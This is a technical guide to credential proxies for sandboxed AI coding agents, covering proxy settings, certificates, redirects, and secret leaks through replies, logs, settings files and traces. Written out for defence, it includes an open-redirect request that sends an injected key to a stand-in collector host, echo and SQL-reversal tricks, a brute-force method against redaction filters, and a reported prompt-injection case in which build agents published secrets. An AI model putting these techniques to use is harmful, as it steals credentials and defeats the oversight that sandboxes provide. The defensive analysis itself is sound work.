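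Approval is less useful when the request is hard to read. Few people can tell whether a 3,000-line change contains private data, and a prompt that summarises the change may leave out the line that contains it. An agent that works overnight has nobody to ask, so the proxy should refuse the risky action and leave it for someone to review in the morning.

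## How client programs break the arrangement

A proxy can apply its rules only to requests that reach it in a form it can read. Ordinary client programs often bypass the proxy, reject its certificate or use a credential they found elsewhere. The error message rarely reveals the cause, so it helps to check the proxy's log first. If the log doesn't show the connection, the client either didn't use the proxy or failed before connecting. If the log shows a connection but no request, the client probably rejected the certificate. If a request got a 401 reply, the HTTP status for a missing or invalid credential, the problem is probably the credential.

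### Programs that ignore the proxy settings

Suppose the operator sets `HTTPS_PROXY` in the coding agent's sandbox and blocks every other route. A request made with the command-line client curl succeeds, but a Node.js script making the same request times out because it ignores the variable and tries to connect directly. If a direct route is still open, the script reaches the service, which rejects its dummy token with a 401 error.

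Node.js reads the standard proxy variables only when the operator also sets `NODE_USE_ENV_PROXY=1` or starts the program with `--use-env-proxy`. This works for all its built-in web functions from versions 22.21.0 and 24.5.0 onward. A library that manages its own connections can still override the setting. Since versions 24.14.0 and 25.4.0, a program can also turn on proxy support from its own code by calling `http.setGlobalProxyFromEnv`.

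In Python, the Requests and HTTPX libraries read the variables by default. The aiohttp library ignores them unless the program passes `trust_env=True`, according to its *Advanced Client Usage*.

The standard web client in Go reads the variables too, with two exceptions. Since Go 1.16, `HTTP_PROXY` has had no effect on `https` addresses, according to a bug report on Go's *net/http*, so the operator has to set `HTTPS_PROXY` as well. Go also never uses a proxy for `localhost`, so the proxy will seem broken in a test against a local server.

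Java takes its proxy from its own settings, such as `https.proxyHost` and `https.proxyPort`, and not from the `http_proxy` environment variable. OpenJDK's *Networking Properties* gives 443 as the default proxy port, which is wrong for most proxies. A user asked in 2004 for Java to read `http_proxy`, and a related request in OpenJDK's bug tracker was still open in late 2025. An operator who can't edit the command that starts a program can put the settings in the `JAVA_TOOL_OPTIONS` environment variable, which Java does read.

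Some Java libraries need their own proxy configuration. Red Hat's *HTTP proxy cannot be configured for Apache HttpClient 4/5 using system properties* describes a user's program that ignored both Java's proxy settings and the environment variables. Older versions of Java's `HttpURLConnection` also tried a direct connection when the proxy failed. OpenJDK's *JDK-8268881* dates the end of this fallback to releases 7u321 and 8u311, but the `sun.net.http.fallbackToDirect` setting can restore it.

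curl's *Proxy environment variables* explains that curl accepts `http_proxy` only in lower case, so it ignores a proxy set in `HTTP_PROXY`. It accepts the other proxy variables in either case. Some web servers turn each header of an incoming request into a variable beginning with `HTTP_`, so if curl read `HTTP_PROXY`, a stranger could send a `Proxy` header and choose the proxy for any script that runs curl.

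The operator can avoid all these differences with transparent redirection, which Vercel's firewall uses. Sandbox0's *API Key Security for AI Agents*, a post by a sandbox vendor, describes a program on each machine that receives the redirected connections and adds the credentials. Transparent redirection is the best default for a sandbox that runs unpredictable software, though clients must still accept the proxy's certificate. Explicit proxy settings are easier to set up when the operator knows every program that will use the proxy.

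Changing the address in the client's settings suits a program that uses one service, but it can fail partway through a task. GitHub's API, for example, returns long lists in pages, and each reply contains the full address of the next page. A client that follows this address goes straight to `https://api.github.com` instead of through the proxy, so the first page arrives but the request for the second fails. The proxy has to rewrite such addresses, or the operator has to use interception instead.

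### Certificates the client won't accept

Adding the proxy's certificate authority to the sandbox operating system's trust store often isn't enough, because many programs have their own. By default, Node.js uses only the Mozilla list bundled with it. The resulting error, `self signed certificate in certificate chain`, looks like a fault in the service. Since versions 22.19.0 and 24.6.0, the operator can make Node.js use the system's list as well.

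| Client | Does it read `HTTPS_PROXY`? | How to make it trust the proxy's authority |
|---|---|---|
| curl on Linux | Yes | Add the authority to the system's list |
| Node.js | Only with `NODE_USE_ENV_PROXY=1` | `NODE_USE_SYSTEM_CA=1` or `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` |
| Python Requests | Yes | `REQUESTS_CA_BUNDLE` |
| Python HTTPX | Yes | `SSL_CERT_FILE` |
| Python aiohttp | Only with `trust_env=True` | Add the authority to the system's list |
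| Go on Linux | Yes | Add the authority to the system's list |
| Java | No | Import the authority into Java's own store with `keytool` |

`NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` adds certificate authorities to the existing list, but `REQUESTS_CA_BUNDLE` replaces the list. The file it names therefore needs the public authorities as well as the proxy's. If it contains only the proxy's authority, intercepted connections succeed, but all connections that the proxy passes through without decrypting them fail.

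Some clients also use certificate pinning, accepting only a particular certificate or key regardless of which authority signed it. A program that pins a certificate with aiohttp stops with the error `FingerprintMismatch` when it receives the proxy's certificate, and changing the trust store doesn't help. If the operator can't remove the pin, interception won't work, and the program needs either an address setting that points to the proxy over plain HTTP or a broker that makes the call for it.

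Many libraries can turn off certificate checks, for example with `ssl=False` in aiohttp. This makes the error disappear, but the client then accepts a certificate from anyone. If the proxy is on another machine, an attacker on the network between the client and the proxy could read the source code that the agent sends or alter the packages it downloads.

A coding agent that gets a certificate error in the sandbox may also write `ssl=False` into the project's code to get past it. If nobody notices, the setting reaches production, where the code may hold a real key and connect without a proxy. Reviewers should treat such a line in an agent's pull request as a security bug.

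### Programs that check the key before using it

A client that rejects its key at start-up never sends a request. It reports an invalid key, and the proxy's log stays empty even though the operator has configured the proxy correctly.

The repair is to give the placeholder whatever the client checks. For a prefix, Docker's `sk-{rand}` template is enough. A client that checks the length needs a placeholder with as many characters as a real key. Some keys also contain a checksum, a few characters computed from the rest so that software can detect typing errors. GitHub's classic tokens have this form:

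```
ghp_ + 30 random characters + 6-character checksum
```

The checksum has 32 bits, so a random ending would be correct about once in 4.3 billion tries. Computing it requires no secret, so a short script can generate a placeholder that passes. But secret scanners use the checksum to recognise real tokens, so they may report a perfect imitation as a leak or block a commit that contains it. It is better to imitate only the features that the client checks.

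Other clients decode the token. A client that expects a JWT may read its expiry time, so the placeholder must be a well-formed JWT with an expiry time in the future. If that time has passed, the client may keep trying to refresh the token.

A client may also test its key with a harmless request, such as `GET /user` on GitHub. If the destination binding covers only pull requests and pushes, this test fails and the program stops. The operator can add the request to the binding after checking what it returns.

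Timing can produce a similar error. Docker applies a secret for one sandbox immediately, but it applies a secret for all sandboxes only to those created afterwards. An operator who adds a missing key for all sandboxes has to recreate the running sandbox before it can use the key.

### Redirects to another host

A service can reply with a redirect, which tells the client to repeat its request at another address. The client then has to decide which headers to send there, and for many years curl sent them all. curl's *CVE-2018-1000007 HTTP authentication leak in redirects* (2018) describes how a user-supplied `Authorization` header went to whatever host the redirect named. Since version 7.58.0, curl's library has sent that header only to the original host unless the user explicitly allows otherwise, according to the notice on the Openwall mailing list (2018).

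Python's Requests library had a narrower flaw in versions before 2.20.0, which kept the Authorization header when a redirect led from HTTPS to plain HTTP on the same host, according to Launchpad's *CVE 2018-18074*. Red Hat's *CVE-2018-18074* explains that anyone able to intercept the traffic could then read the credential.

Current versions of curl and Requests drop the `Authorization` header when a redirect leads to a different host, but mistakes still occur in special cases. *CVE-2026-3783 token leak with redirect and netrc* (2026) describes a flaw in curl versions 7.33.0 to 8.18.0. They could pass an OAuth token to a second host if the user's netrc file, which lists usernames and passwords by host, had an entry for that host or a default entry. *CVE-2025-14524 bearer token leak on cross-protocol redirect* (2026) describes a curl flaw that could leak a token on redirects to mail and directory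 servers, though curl follows those redirects only if the user enables them.

The protection also depends on the header's name. Both programs treat `x-api-key`, which Anthropic's API uses, as an ordinary header and send it to the new host too.

A client behind a credential proxy has only a dummy value to leak, but the proxy can make the same mistake with the real one. Suppose an approved service has a page that forwards visitors to any address, and hostile code sends this request:

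```
GET /go?to=https://collector.example/ HTTP/1.1
Host: api.example.com
x-api-key: not-a-real-key
```

The proxy adds the real key, and the service replies with a redirect to `collector.example`. If the proxy follows the redirect itself, its HTTP library sends the `x-api-key` header to the new address, and the attacker receives the key. The connection to `collector.example` may also bypass the allowlist, because the request did not come from the sandbox.

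The proxy should return the redirect to the client instead. The client then makes a new request, and the proxy checks its destination against the allowlist and the binding as usual. Many HTTP libraries follow redirects by default, so anyone writing a proxy has to turn this off. A proxy that must follow redirects has to repeat both checks and choose the credential again at every hop.

Many services redirect large downloads to a storage host such as S3, with a signature in the new address. If the proxy also adds the original service's token, S3 rejects the request because it contains two forms of authentication. To prevent this common error, the operator should put the storage host on the allowlist but leave it out of the token's binding.

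### Credentials the client finds elsewhere

If a program finds another credential in the sandbox, it may use that one instead of the placeholder. The Python library Requests reads the user's netrc file automatically, and a matching entry replaces the `Authorization` header that the program set. The service may then reject the request with a 401 or accept it under an unexpected account. If the operator has shared the developer's home directory with the sandbox, the netrc file may also contain real passwords.

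Versions of Requests before 2.32.4 could send passwords from the netrc file to the wrong host when given a specially written URL, according to OSV's *CVE-2024-47081* (2025). One suggested workaround was to supply explicit credentials with each call, but Wilk, in *CVE-2024-47081*, objected that this fails after a redirect because Requests checks the netrc file again for the new address. Setting `trust_env=False` stops Requests from using the netrc file, but also makes it ignore the proxy variables. Upgrading Requests and keeping netrc files out of the sandbox avoids both problems.

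Git can get passwords from a credential helper, a separate program that stores or supplies them. Git usually first sends a request without a password and calls the helper only if the server returns a 401 error. If the proxy fails to add the token, Git may get the developer's real password from the helper. The push then succeeds, so nobody notices that the proxy isn't working or that a real password has entered the sandbox. Some development tools automatically share the host's helper with containers, so the operator should check Git's settings from inside the sandbox.

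AWS's libraries search several places for a key and can end up using the machine's role credentials from the metadata service. A dummy key in the environment variables stops the search before it reaches the metadata service, and a signing proxy can then replace the signature made with the dummy key.

When Docker has both an API key and an OAuth login for a service, it uses the API key. The provider may therefore bill a developer's work to the API key even though the developer has logged in with a subscription. Removing the stored key makes Docker use the login.

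AI agents can also search for credentials unprompted, as NordLayer's coding assistant did when a configuration file was missing. An agent that gets a 401 may likewise look for another token. Sandbox0 blocks a request by default when its proxy can't get the credential, because a clear connection error is easier to diagnose than a 401 from the service. The proxy can also return a short message with the name of the missing secret and an instruction to stop and tell the operator. This may help with a cooperative agent, but the only protection against hostile code is to have no other credentials for it to find.

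Replacing a key can start the same search. Sandbox0's proxy keeps a copy of each credential in memory, by default until the proxy restarts, so it may keep sending the old key after the operator has cancelled it. The agent then gets a 401. Setting a short time limit on the copy, such as one minute, prevents this.

### WebSockets, gRPC and long streams

Some clients bypass the proxy for WebSocket connections, which begin as ordinary HTTP requests and then become two-way message channels. EunHyunsu (2026) reported in *RFR*, a proposed change to Java, that Java's default proxy selector returns a direct connection for WebSocket addresses. A reply in the same discussion (OpenJDK, *RFR*) pointed out that Java's own WebSocket client avoids this by looking up the HTTP proxy itself, so the problem mainly affects other Java libraries. According to ManKier's *libcurl-env*, curl's library checks `ws_proxy`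 or `wss_proxy` first and then falls back to the ordinary proxy variables.

Other WebSocket connections open normally and break later. One Node.js user, evan966890, reported that connections to the chat service Discord dropped after minutes or hours with proxy support on, but stayed up without it. A proxy that closes idle connections can also cause this symptom. To prevent idle closures, the operator can raise the proxy's idle timeout or have the client send regular pings.

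Discord also requires a bot's token in a message sent after the connection opens, so injecting headers isn't enough. The proxy would have to parse the service's messages to add the token. Sandbox0's proxy does this for two other protocols. For the Redis database, it sends a login command before the client's first command. For MQTT, a messaging protocol common in connected devices, it adds a username and password to the opening message.

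gRPC, a system for calling functions on another computer, runs over HTTP/2, which carries many requests over one connection. Sandbox0 says that its header injection works for gRPC as it does for HTTPS. For this to work, a proxy has to support HTTP/2 on both of its connections. If it offers only the older HTTP/1.1, most web clients adapt, but gRPC calls fail.

The proxy also has to forward HTTP trailers, the headers that follow the body, because gRPC puts the result status there. If the proxy drops them, a call that succeeded appears to have failed, and a client that retries may perform the same action twice. Some gRPC libraries also have their own trust store, which the operator can replace by setting `GRPC_DEFAULT_SSL_ROOTS_FILE_PATH`.

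An HTTP/2 client may reuse a connection for a second host if the server's certificate covers both names. The proxy can prevent this by putting only one host name in each certificate it makes.

Language models often send their replies in small pieces over several minutes. If the proxy waits for the complete reply before forwarding it, the agent appears to freeze and may time out. The operator should turn off response buffering for these connections and set a timeout that allows for long pauses while the model works.

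## Leaks through responses and logs

A secret can enter the sandbox even when the client, the proxy and the network rules all work correctly. After the proxy adds a token to a request, the service's reply goes back to the sandbox, where hostile code can read anything in it. The reply may contain the token itself or a secret that the service has just created. Either can end up in a log and stay there long after the sandbox is gone.

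### How a service can send a secret back

Reflection occurs when a service's response repeats a secret that the proxy put in the request. The simplest cause is an echo endpoint, a page that returns whatever request it receives, which developers use for debugging. Suppose an internal service has one, and the proxy adds a key to every request for that host. Hostile code sends this:

```
GET /debug/headers HTTP/1.1
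Host: reports.example.com
X-Api-Key: not-a-real-key
```

The service replies:

```
HTTP/1.1 200 OK
Content-Type: application/json

{"Host": "reports.example.com", "X-Api-Key": "rk_live_…"}
```

Header injection doesn't prevent this, because the proxy put the right key in the right header for the right host. A server that supports the HTTP `TRACE` method also returns the request it received. Most public services turn `TRACE` off, but an old internal server may still support it.

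Error messages can also leak a key, because a service that rejects a key may quote it, as in `Invalid API key: rk_live_…`. The leak does little harm if the key has expired, but a service can also reject a working key, for example because it belongs to another region or lacks a permission.

When a service takes its key in the URL, even successful replies can repeat it. If the service redirects the client to the same address with a slash at the end, the `Location` header may contain the whole URL, including the key. A long list that arrives in pages can have the same problem:

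```
{"results": […], "next": "https://api.example.com/series?page=2&api_key=8f1c…"}
```

If the proxy replaces placeholders in request bodies, hostile code can also save the secret at the service and read it back later, as in the gist example. The request that reads it back may go to a different host. GitHub serves the raw text of gists from `gist.githubusercontent.com`, which needs no token for a public gist, so a proxy that decrypts only connections that need a credential would not detect the secret in the response.

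### Replies that contain new secrets

Some services create secrets and return them in normal operation. The proxy has no record of these secrets, so it can't detect them by matching their values.

| Reply | Example | What a thief can do with the secret |
|---|---|---|
| Token endpoint | OAuth access and refresh tokens | Use the account until the tokens expire or someone cancels them |
| Key-creation call | AWS's `CreateAccessKey` | Use the new key until someone deletes it |
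| Presigned link | A temporary address for a file in S3 | Read or write that file until the link expires |
| Session cookie | A `Set-Cookie` header after a login | Act as the logged-in user until the session ends |

Key creation is the most dangerous because the new key can outlast the sandbox and the original credential. An operator who discovers the attack and replaces the stored AWS key may not notice that the attacker has created a second one. Hostile code can get the same lasting access without receiving any secret, by adding the attacker's SSH public key to a repository. The reply then contains no secret to detect, so the proxy has to block the request.

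Presigned links are harder to avoid because the coding agent may need replies that contain them to do its normal work. When a program asks GitHub's API about a file in a private repository, the reply includes a temporary download address that works without the developer's token. An operator can reasonably accept this risk, since the agent can already read the file.

The proxy can keep session cookies out of the sandbox. It removes the `Set-Cookie` header from the reply, stores the cookie, and adds it to that sandbox's later requests to the same host. Programs that read the cookie themselves won't work with this arrangement.

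### Keeping secrets out of replies

The strongest defence is to put the secret only in the header where the service expects it, since few services include authentication headers in their replies. An echo endpoint can still leak the secret, and this defence isn't possible for services that accept a key only in the URL.

The next strongest defense is to block the endpoints that return secrets. If the operator's rules allow only the methods and paths the agent needs, they block `TRACE`, `/debug/headers` and key-creation calls by default. A list of forbidden endpoints works only if the operator knows every endpoint that might repeat a header. Narrow permissions also help, since AWS rejects key-creation requests from a role that lacks permission to make them.

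When the agent needs an endpoint that returns a secret, the proxy can replace the secret in the reply, as Docker's does for OAuth logins. To do this, the proxy must know the reply's exact format. If the service renames `access_token` or moves it into a nested field, a rule written for the old format will miss the token and let it through to the agent. The proxy should therefore block token endpoint replies that it can't fully interpret.

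The weakest defence is to search every reply for known secrets and remove them. This is easy to add because it requires no knowledge of the service, but a secret can get past the search in many ways.

### Why a response filter misses secrets

A proxy receives a long reply in chunks. If one chunk ends after the first 25 bytes of a 40-byte GitHub token, neither that chunk nor the next contains the whole token, so a filter that checks each chunk separately lets both through.

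The filter therefore has to keep the end of each chunk until the next one arrives. An unfinished token can be at most one byte short of complete, so the filter must hold back

40 − 1 = 39 bytes.

A filter that checks for several secrets must hold back enough bytes for the longest one. Always holding back 39 bytes can stall a two-way connection, because a client that waits for the end of a message before answering may never receive it. A better filter holds back the end of a chunk only when it matches the beginning of a secret. If a secret begins with `ghp_7Q`, the filter would hold back those characters at the end of a chunk but immediately release a chunk ending in `hello`.

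This still fails for the streamed replies of language models, which divide the text among many small messages:

```
data: {"text": "ghp_7Qm"}

data: {"text": "x2Lk"}
```

Each message has its own punctuation and labels, so the token's characters are no longer next to each other. To find the token, the filter has to parse the provider's format, extract the text from every message, and join it.

Hostile code can also split a secret between replies so that no single reply contains all of it. HTTP lets a client request part of a file, so if the secret is in a stored file, the code can fetch the secret's first 20 bytes in one request and the rest in another.

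Removing fragments as well as whole secrets makes matters worse. Suppose the filter removes any eight-character piece of a GitHub token. Hostile code can send guesses to a service that repeats ordinary text, and see which ones disappear. Classic tokens begin with `ghp_`, so the first piece has four unknown characters, each with 62 possible values:

62^4 ≈ 14.8 million guesses.

With a separator after each guess, a one-megabyte reply can test about 111,000 guesses, so roughly 133 replies are enough. The code then finds the other 32 characters one at a time, with at most 62 guesses for each, or 1,984 in total. A filter that removes only whole tokens doesn't have this weakness, because the code would have to guess every unknown character at once. The code could still guess a short password, so the operator should replace it with a long random one.

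Encoding creates more forms to search for. Base64 turns each group of three bytes into four characters, so the result depends on where in a group the secret begins. For example, the word `secret` has three encoded forms:

| Text before `secret` | Encoded result | Part that depends only on `secret` |
|---|---|---|
| None | `c2VjcmV0` | `c2VjcmV0` |
| One byte, `x` | `eHNlY3JldA==` | `NlY3Jld` |
| Two bytes, `xx` | `eHhzZWNyZXQ=` | `zZWNyZX` |

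The characters at the edges can mix bits from the secret and the neighbouring text, so the filter has to search for the part in the last column. For a 40-byte token, that part has 53, 52 or 53 characters, depending on the position, and the filter must be ready to hold back 52 characters. A secret can also appear in Base64 without an attacker encoding it. Git uses HTTP Basic authentication over HTTPS, so an echo of its login header contains the token only in Base64.

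URL-safe Base64 replaces two of the standard characters, and email software inserts line breaks into long Base64 text. Hexadecimal and URL encoding need their own patterns, as does a secret encoded twice.

The proxy can't find the token by searching a compressed reply, and clients normally tell a service that they accept compressed replies. The proxy can change the request's `Accept-Encoding` header to `identity`, which asks for an uncompressed reply. If the service compresses the reply anyway, the proxy has to decompress it before searching, or refuse it. Neither measure helps with a file that was already compressed, such as a ZIP archive, unless the filter also opens the archive.

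Hostile code may also be able to make the service return the secret in a disguised form. Vercel's first Snowflake proxy replaced placeholders anywhere in the request body, so generated code could have run `SELECT REVERSE('<placeholder>')`. The database would have returned the token backwards, and a filter for the token would have missed it. Filtering for a list of known encodings as well can't fully prevent this, because no list covers every way a database or a language model can transform a string.

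### What redaction still catches

Redaction is still useful because most accidental reflections, such as those in error messages, debugging pages and `next` links, repeat the key exactly as the proxy sent it. A long random token almost never appears by chance, so a match is strong evidence of a leak.

When the filter finds a secret, it should replace the secret with the placeholder, correct the reply's `Content-Length` and alert the operator. The client then sees the string it sent. The operator can block the endpoint and check whether earlier replies from it reached a sandbox before the filter was running. If they did, the key needs replacing.

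For newly created secrets, the filter can only look for recognisable formats, such as strings that begin with `ghp_`. This misses passwords and catches harmless example keys. If the agent downloads a source file containing an example key, the filter changes the file, and the agent may commit the changed version without noticing. For unknown secrets, an alert is often better than automatic replacement.

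### What the proxy should log

A credential proxy handles two versions of each request, one from the sandbox and one with the real secret. It should log the sandbox's version before adding the secret, and afterwards record what it decided and how the service responded. Logs of the outgoing requests would contain every key the proxy uses. For a Telegram bot, even a basic access log of those requests would contain the token, because it is in the URL path.

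Debug logs can expose credentials. Some proxies mask the `Authorization` header automatically but print `x-api-key` in full, and an operator investigating a fault may turn on a mode that logs whole requests. It is safer to reproduce the fault with a test account and a canary secret, which is a fake secret with a recognisable value.

The sandbox's version of a request can contain real secrets as well. A client may have found a password in a netrc file, or a login may have put a session token in a query string. The proxy should therefore leave out headers, bodies and the values in query strings, and keep only the fields that someone will need during an investigation:

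```
{
  "time": "2026-12-03T09:14:07Z",
  "sandbox": "fix-rounding",
  "method": "POST",
  "host": "api.github.com",
  "path": "/repos/acme/shop/pulls",
  "rule": "open-pull-request",
  "secret": "github-token-acme-shop",
  "secret_version": 4,
  "result": "secret added",
  "status": 201,
  "bytes_sent": 212,
  "bytes_received": 5120
}
```

After a leak, an operator can use the `secret` field to find where the proxy sent that key and for which sandboxes. The log in Docker's kit flaw didn't show this, because an entry recorded the connection but not the added key. The version number shows whether a request used the key from before or after a replacement. The byte counts can reveal an unusually large upload without the log storing its contents.

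A log entry doesn't need to include the secret's value, and logs often have more readers than the secret store and last longer. A hash isn't a safe substitute, because anyone who reads the log can guess a weak password and check the guess against the hash. Docker prints the first and last few characters of each stored secret when a developer lists them. That is reasonable for a long token on the developer's own screen, but in a log the name and version identify the secret just as well.

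The proxy should log refused requests too, including any attempt to send a placeholder to an unapproved host. It should write entries in a format that encodes line breaks, such as JSON. Otherwise, hostile code could forge a second entry by putting a line break in a request path. The sandbox should have no access to the log.

The operator's own commands can also expose secrets. Docker warns that typing a custom secret after `--value` saves it in the shell's history and makes it visible to other programs that the same user runs. Docker can instead fetch a secret by running a command, but it stores the command's text, so that text shouldn't contain a secret either. If the fetch fails, Docker normally hides the command's error output because it may contain sensitive information. The `--show-error` option displays that output, so using it in an automated build may put the secret in the build log.

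A crash can expose secrets that a proxy keeps out of its logs. When a program fails, the operating system may save its memory to a file called a core dump, and a proxy's core dump can contain every secret it was holding. Error-reporting services can also collect secrets when they upload the values of a program's variables along with the error. The operator should turn off core dumps for the proxy and keep variables and request headers out of its error reports.

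### Build agents that publish their own output

Many projects run AI agents in continuous integration (CI), the automated system that builds and tests each proposed change. These agents read text from strangers, and on a public project anyone can read their output.

In July 2026, Novee Security showed how this combination can leak secrets. Help Net Security's *An AI agent can pass every safety check and still leak secrets* describes tests by Novee engineer Elad Meged on the agents that Anthropic, Google and OpenAI ran on their own repositories. An agent read a stranger's bug report, took commands from it, got them approved and posted the output in the public discussion. Anthropic's system leaked secrets this way. One part approved a command because it looked harmless, and another published the output by default.

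Anthropic fixed each problem Meged reported and paid him for it, but he kept finding new routes. The last one needed no connection to an attacker's server. Controls on outbound connections can't stop this kind of leak, because the agent is supposed to post to the project's public page. Meged found related weaknesses in the Google and OpenAI tools, where a later stage failed to apply a restriction or trusted data left by an earlier stage. These were a researcher's demonstrations, and the article doesn't report that criminals had used them.

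Microsoft separately found that Claude Code's GitHub workflow protected secrets from shell commands but not from the agent's file-reading tool. The tool could read the workflow's API key and possibly other credentials on the build machine. Anthropic fixed this in version 2.1.128. Microsoft began the research after seeing attempted prompt injections in public repositories that use such agents.

Build systems often mask known secrets in their logs, but like other redaction, this misses secrets that are encoded or split up. It also may not cover comments that the agent posts through the code host's API. If the key is in a credential proxy on another machine, the agent has no key to publish. Meged advises operators to trace where an agent's output goes next and check whether the next stage publishes it, loads it as configuration or passes it to a more powerful tool.

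### Secrets in saved Claude Code settings

Agents also keep records on the developer's computer. When Claude Code asks permission to run a command, the developer can choose "Yes, and don't ask again." Claude Code then saves the approval in the project folder, in a file named `.claude/settings.local.json`. The file might contain these two rules:

```
"allow": [
  "Bash(npm test:*)",
  "Bash(psql postgres://shop:k3Vd9…@db.example.com/orders)"
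]
```

The first rule is a pattern that covers any command beginning with `npm test`. The second is an exact command that includes the database password.

Apiiro, a security company, searched public GitHub for copies of this file from 1 to 3 November 2026. Reed (2026) describes the method in *SecBlog Weekly 011*. Apiiro counted a string as a real secret if an AI reviewer accepted it and it either had the format of a known provider's key or was a password beside a public host name. Apiiro didn't test whether the secrets worked, but one organisation it notified confirmed that its key did.

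| What Apiiro counted | Number |
|---|---|
| Public copies of the settings file | 104,185, in 103,617 repositories |
| Copies with at least one real secret | 1,122 (1.1%) |
| Different secrets in those copies | 1,379 |
| Different secrets after adding file histories, shared settings and saved transcripts | 2,539, in 1,994 repositories |

InfoQ's *Claude Code Has Been Leaking Secrets through its "Don't Ask Again" Feature* (2026) mistakenly gives the number of files, 1,122, as the number of secrets. According to iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets*, Apiiro reproduced the behaviour with two current models and concluded that Claude Code, not the model, caused it.

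Claude Code tries to keep the file off GitHub by adding it to a list of files that Git ignores. But GitLab's *How to prevent leaks from Claude Code's 'Don't ask again' file* explains that this list is stored on the developer's computer, so it has no effect when someone copies the project to another machine. Boris Cherny, who leads Claude Code at Anthropic, replied that people must have created the exposed files by hand and committed them. He also said his team was looking for ways to prevent the problem.

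GitGuardian disputes that explanation. Infobae's *El asistente de programación de Anthropic dejó contraseñas y claves* (2026) reports that in all of the about 3,000 occurrences GitGuardian reviewed, the secret was in a rule with the exact form that the permission prompt produces. This is good evidence that Claude Code wrote the rules, though it doesn't show who committed the files. Apiiro traced 1,105 of the affected repositories and found that in 539, a commit naming Claude as co-author had changed the file.

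GitGuardian also counted everything uploaded between January 2025 and 7 November 2026, even if the owner later deleted it. This gave a much larger total of 31,088 different credentials, of which 5,343 worked when GitGuardian detected them. The monthly number peaked at 12,535 in April 2026 and fell to 959 in October, for reasons GitGuardian doesn't know.

The settings file also leaks through public npm packages and Docker images. In April 2026, the security company Lakera examined about 46,500 npm packages and found the file in 428 of them, according to TechTalks' *Claude Code is leaking API keys into public package registries* (2026). Thirty of the packages contained credentials. GitGuardian found 613 secrets from such files in public Docker Hub images, including one token that appeared in 559 versions of the same image.

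Of Apiiro's 1,122 files, the secret scanner gitleaks flagged 564 and TruffleHog flagged 643. Together they flagged 907 and missed 215, or about 19%. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners' secrets on GitHub* quotes Apiiro's explanation that scanners look for a provider's prefix or a long random string, while a password typed into a command looks like any other word.

With a placeholder, the saved command would contain only a worthless string. But more than a third of the secrets Apiiro found opened a database directly, and most database passwords need a protocol broker instead of a placeholder. Developers who have neither can put a variable such as `$DB_URL` in the command, so that Claude Code saves the variable's name and not its value. They can also approve patterns instead of exact commands. Anyone who has already committed a secret has to replace it, because deleting the file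 leaves the secret in Git's history and in other people's copies.

### Transcripts and traces

An agent's transcript is the saved record of a session, including the user's messages, the commands the agent ran and their output. If the agent printed a token, the token stays in the transcript after the sandbox is gone. Apiiro also found secrets in agents' memory files and in notes left by one session for the next. Criminals collect these files too. Reed describes a report by the security company SpyCloud on Aoki, a program that steals the local session folders of Claude Code, Codex and other AI tools.

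Some tools upload more than the user expects. Sonar describes a researcher who put a fake API key and a fake database password in a project and watched the network traffic of xAI's coding agent, Grok Build. The agent uploaded the whole repository to cloud storage, with both secrets in plain text.

Developers also send records of an agent's work to monitoring services on purpose. Such a record, called a trace, lists the steps the agent took and may include complete requests. In a placeholder design, part of a trace might look like this:

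```
{
  "step": "create pull request",
  "url": "https://api.github.com/repos/acme/shop/pulls",
  "headers": {"Authorization": "Bearer ph_7f3a…"}
}
```

The trace contains only the placeholder, so it is safe to store, but the agent uploads it through the same proxy as its other requests. If the proxy replaces the placeholder in the upload, it puts the real GitHub token into the monitoring service's database, where everyone with access to the traces can read it.

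Destination binding normally prevents this, since the monitoring service isn't on the token's host list. It fails when one host both accepts the key and stores traces. For example, OpenAI's software for building agents sends traces by default to `api.openai.com`, which also receives the OpenAI key. The proxy must therefore put the real key in the upload's `Authorization` header but leave the placeholder in the body unchanged.

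A proxy that blocks every request carrying a placeholder to an unapproved host also blocks trace uploads to a monitoring service, so the developer loses the trace. *Sandboxes that lie about their secrets* therefore treats trace uploads as a separate case, in which the proxy forwards the placeholder unchanged as harmless text. The operator should limit this exception to the monitoring service, so that a placeholder sent to any other unapproved host still raises an alarm.

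microsandbox's predictable placeholders have an advantage here, because `$MSB_OPENAI_API_KEY` in a trace shows which secret the program tried to use. With random placeholders, the operator can match the trace to the proxy's log by time and sandbox. If the proxy produces traces of its own, they need the same rule as its log, since a trace of the outgoing request contains the real secret.

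## A worked deployment: choosing, configuring and testing

Suppose a company called Acme wants its coding agent to work on `acme/shop` overnight. The agent calls a language model, downloads packages from Acme's private registry, reads test files from an S3 bucket, runs tests against a copy of the orders database, and opens a pull request on GitHub. It needs a credential for each of these five services.

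The agent runs with administrator rights in a virtual machine. A credential proxy and a database broker run on a second machine, and firewall rules outside the sandbox let the agent reach only those two services. The host opens a separate encrypted tunnel for each sandbox, so the proxy and the broker can identify which sandbox is calling.

### Choosing an arrangement for each credential

Acme should first ask whether the agent needs each credential. In the Agent Authenticator paper, Ganesan lists permissions that exceed or outlast the task among the causes of the five incidents. If the tests could use invented data in a database inside the sandbox, Acme could drop the database password. In this deployment, the agent needs all five credentials, and the way each service authenticates largely determines the choice of method.

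| Credential | Arrangement | Reason | Remaining risk |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model API key | Header injection, with a spending limit | The service reads the key from one fixed header | Hostile code can spend up to the limit and send source code to the provider |
| GitHub token | Header injection, with a token for one repository | Git and GitHub's API both read the `Authorization` header | Hostile code can push harmful changes or put private data in a pull request |
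| Package-registry token | Header injection, for downloads only | The agent never publishes packages | Malicious packages still run in the sandbox, and a flaw in the registry could open a way out |
| Access to the S3 bucket | A signing proxy with its own workload identity | AWS expects a signature, and nobody has to store a key | Hostile code can read every file the role can read |
| Database password | A protocol broker with a read-only account | The login doesn't use HTTP | Hostile code can read every table the account can read |

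The GitHub token needs two rules because GitHub's API accepts it after the word `Bearer`, while Git sends it in HTTP Basic format. Acme can register the agent as a GitHub App, a separate identity whose access tokens expire after an hour. The proxy then has to protect the private key it uses to request those tokens.

In July 2026, the OpenAI agent that later broke into Hugging Face escaped its sandbox within an hour. According to GitLab (2026), it exploited a vulnerability in a package proxy on its allowlist. The registry poses a similar risk, so Acme should promptly install the registry's security updates and restrict the registry's outbound connections.

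The database needs a broker because its traffic may never reach a web proxy. In Cloudflare's sandboxes, for example, the code that adds credentials receives only HTTP and HTTPS requests. PostgreSQL traffic normally uses port 5432 and bypasses that code.

### Rules for the model key and the bucket

A working rule can be very short. In ZenML's *Credential proxy*, a tutorial from a company that makes software for AI workflows, the rule contains only a host, a header and a reference to the stored secret. But ZenML warns that the proxy then adds the token to every request for that host, whatever the method or path. Acme's rule for the model key is stricter:

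```
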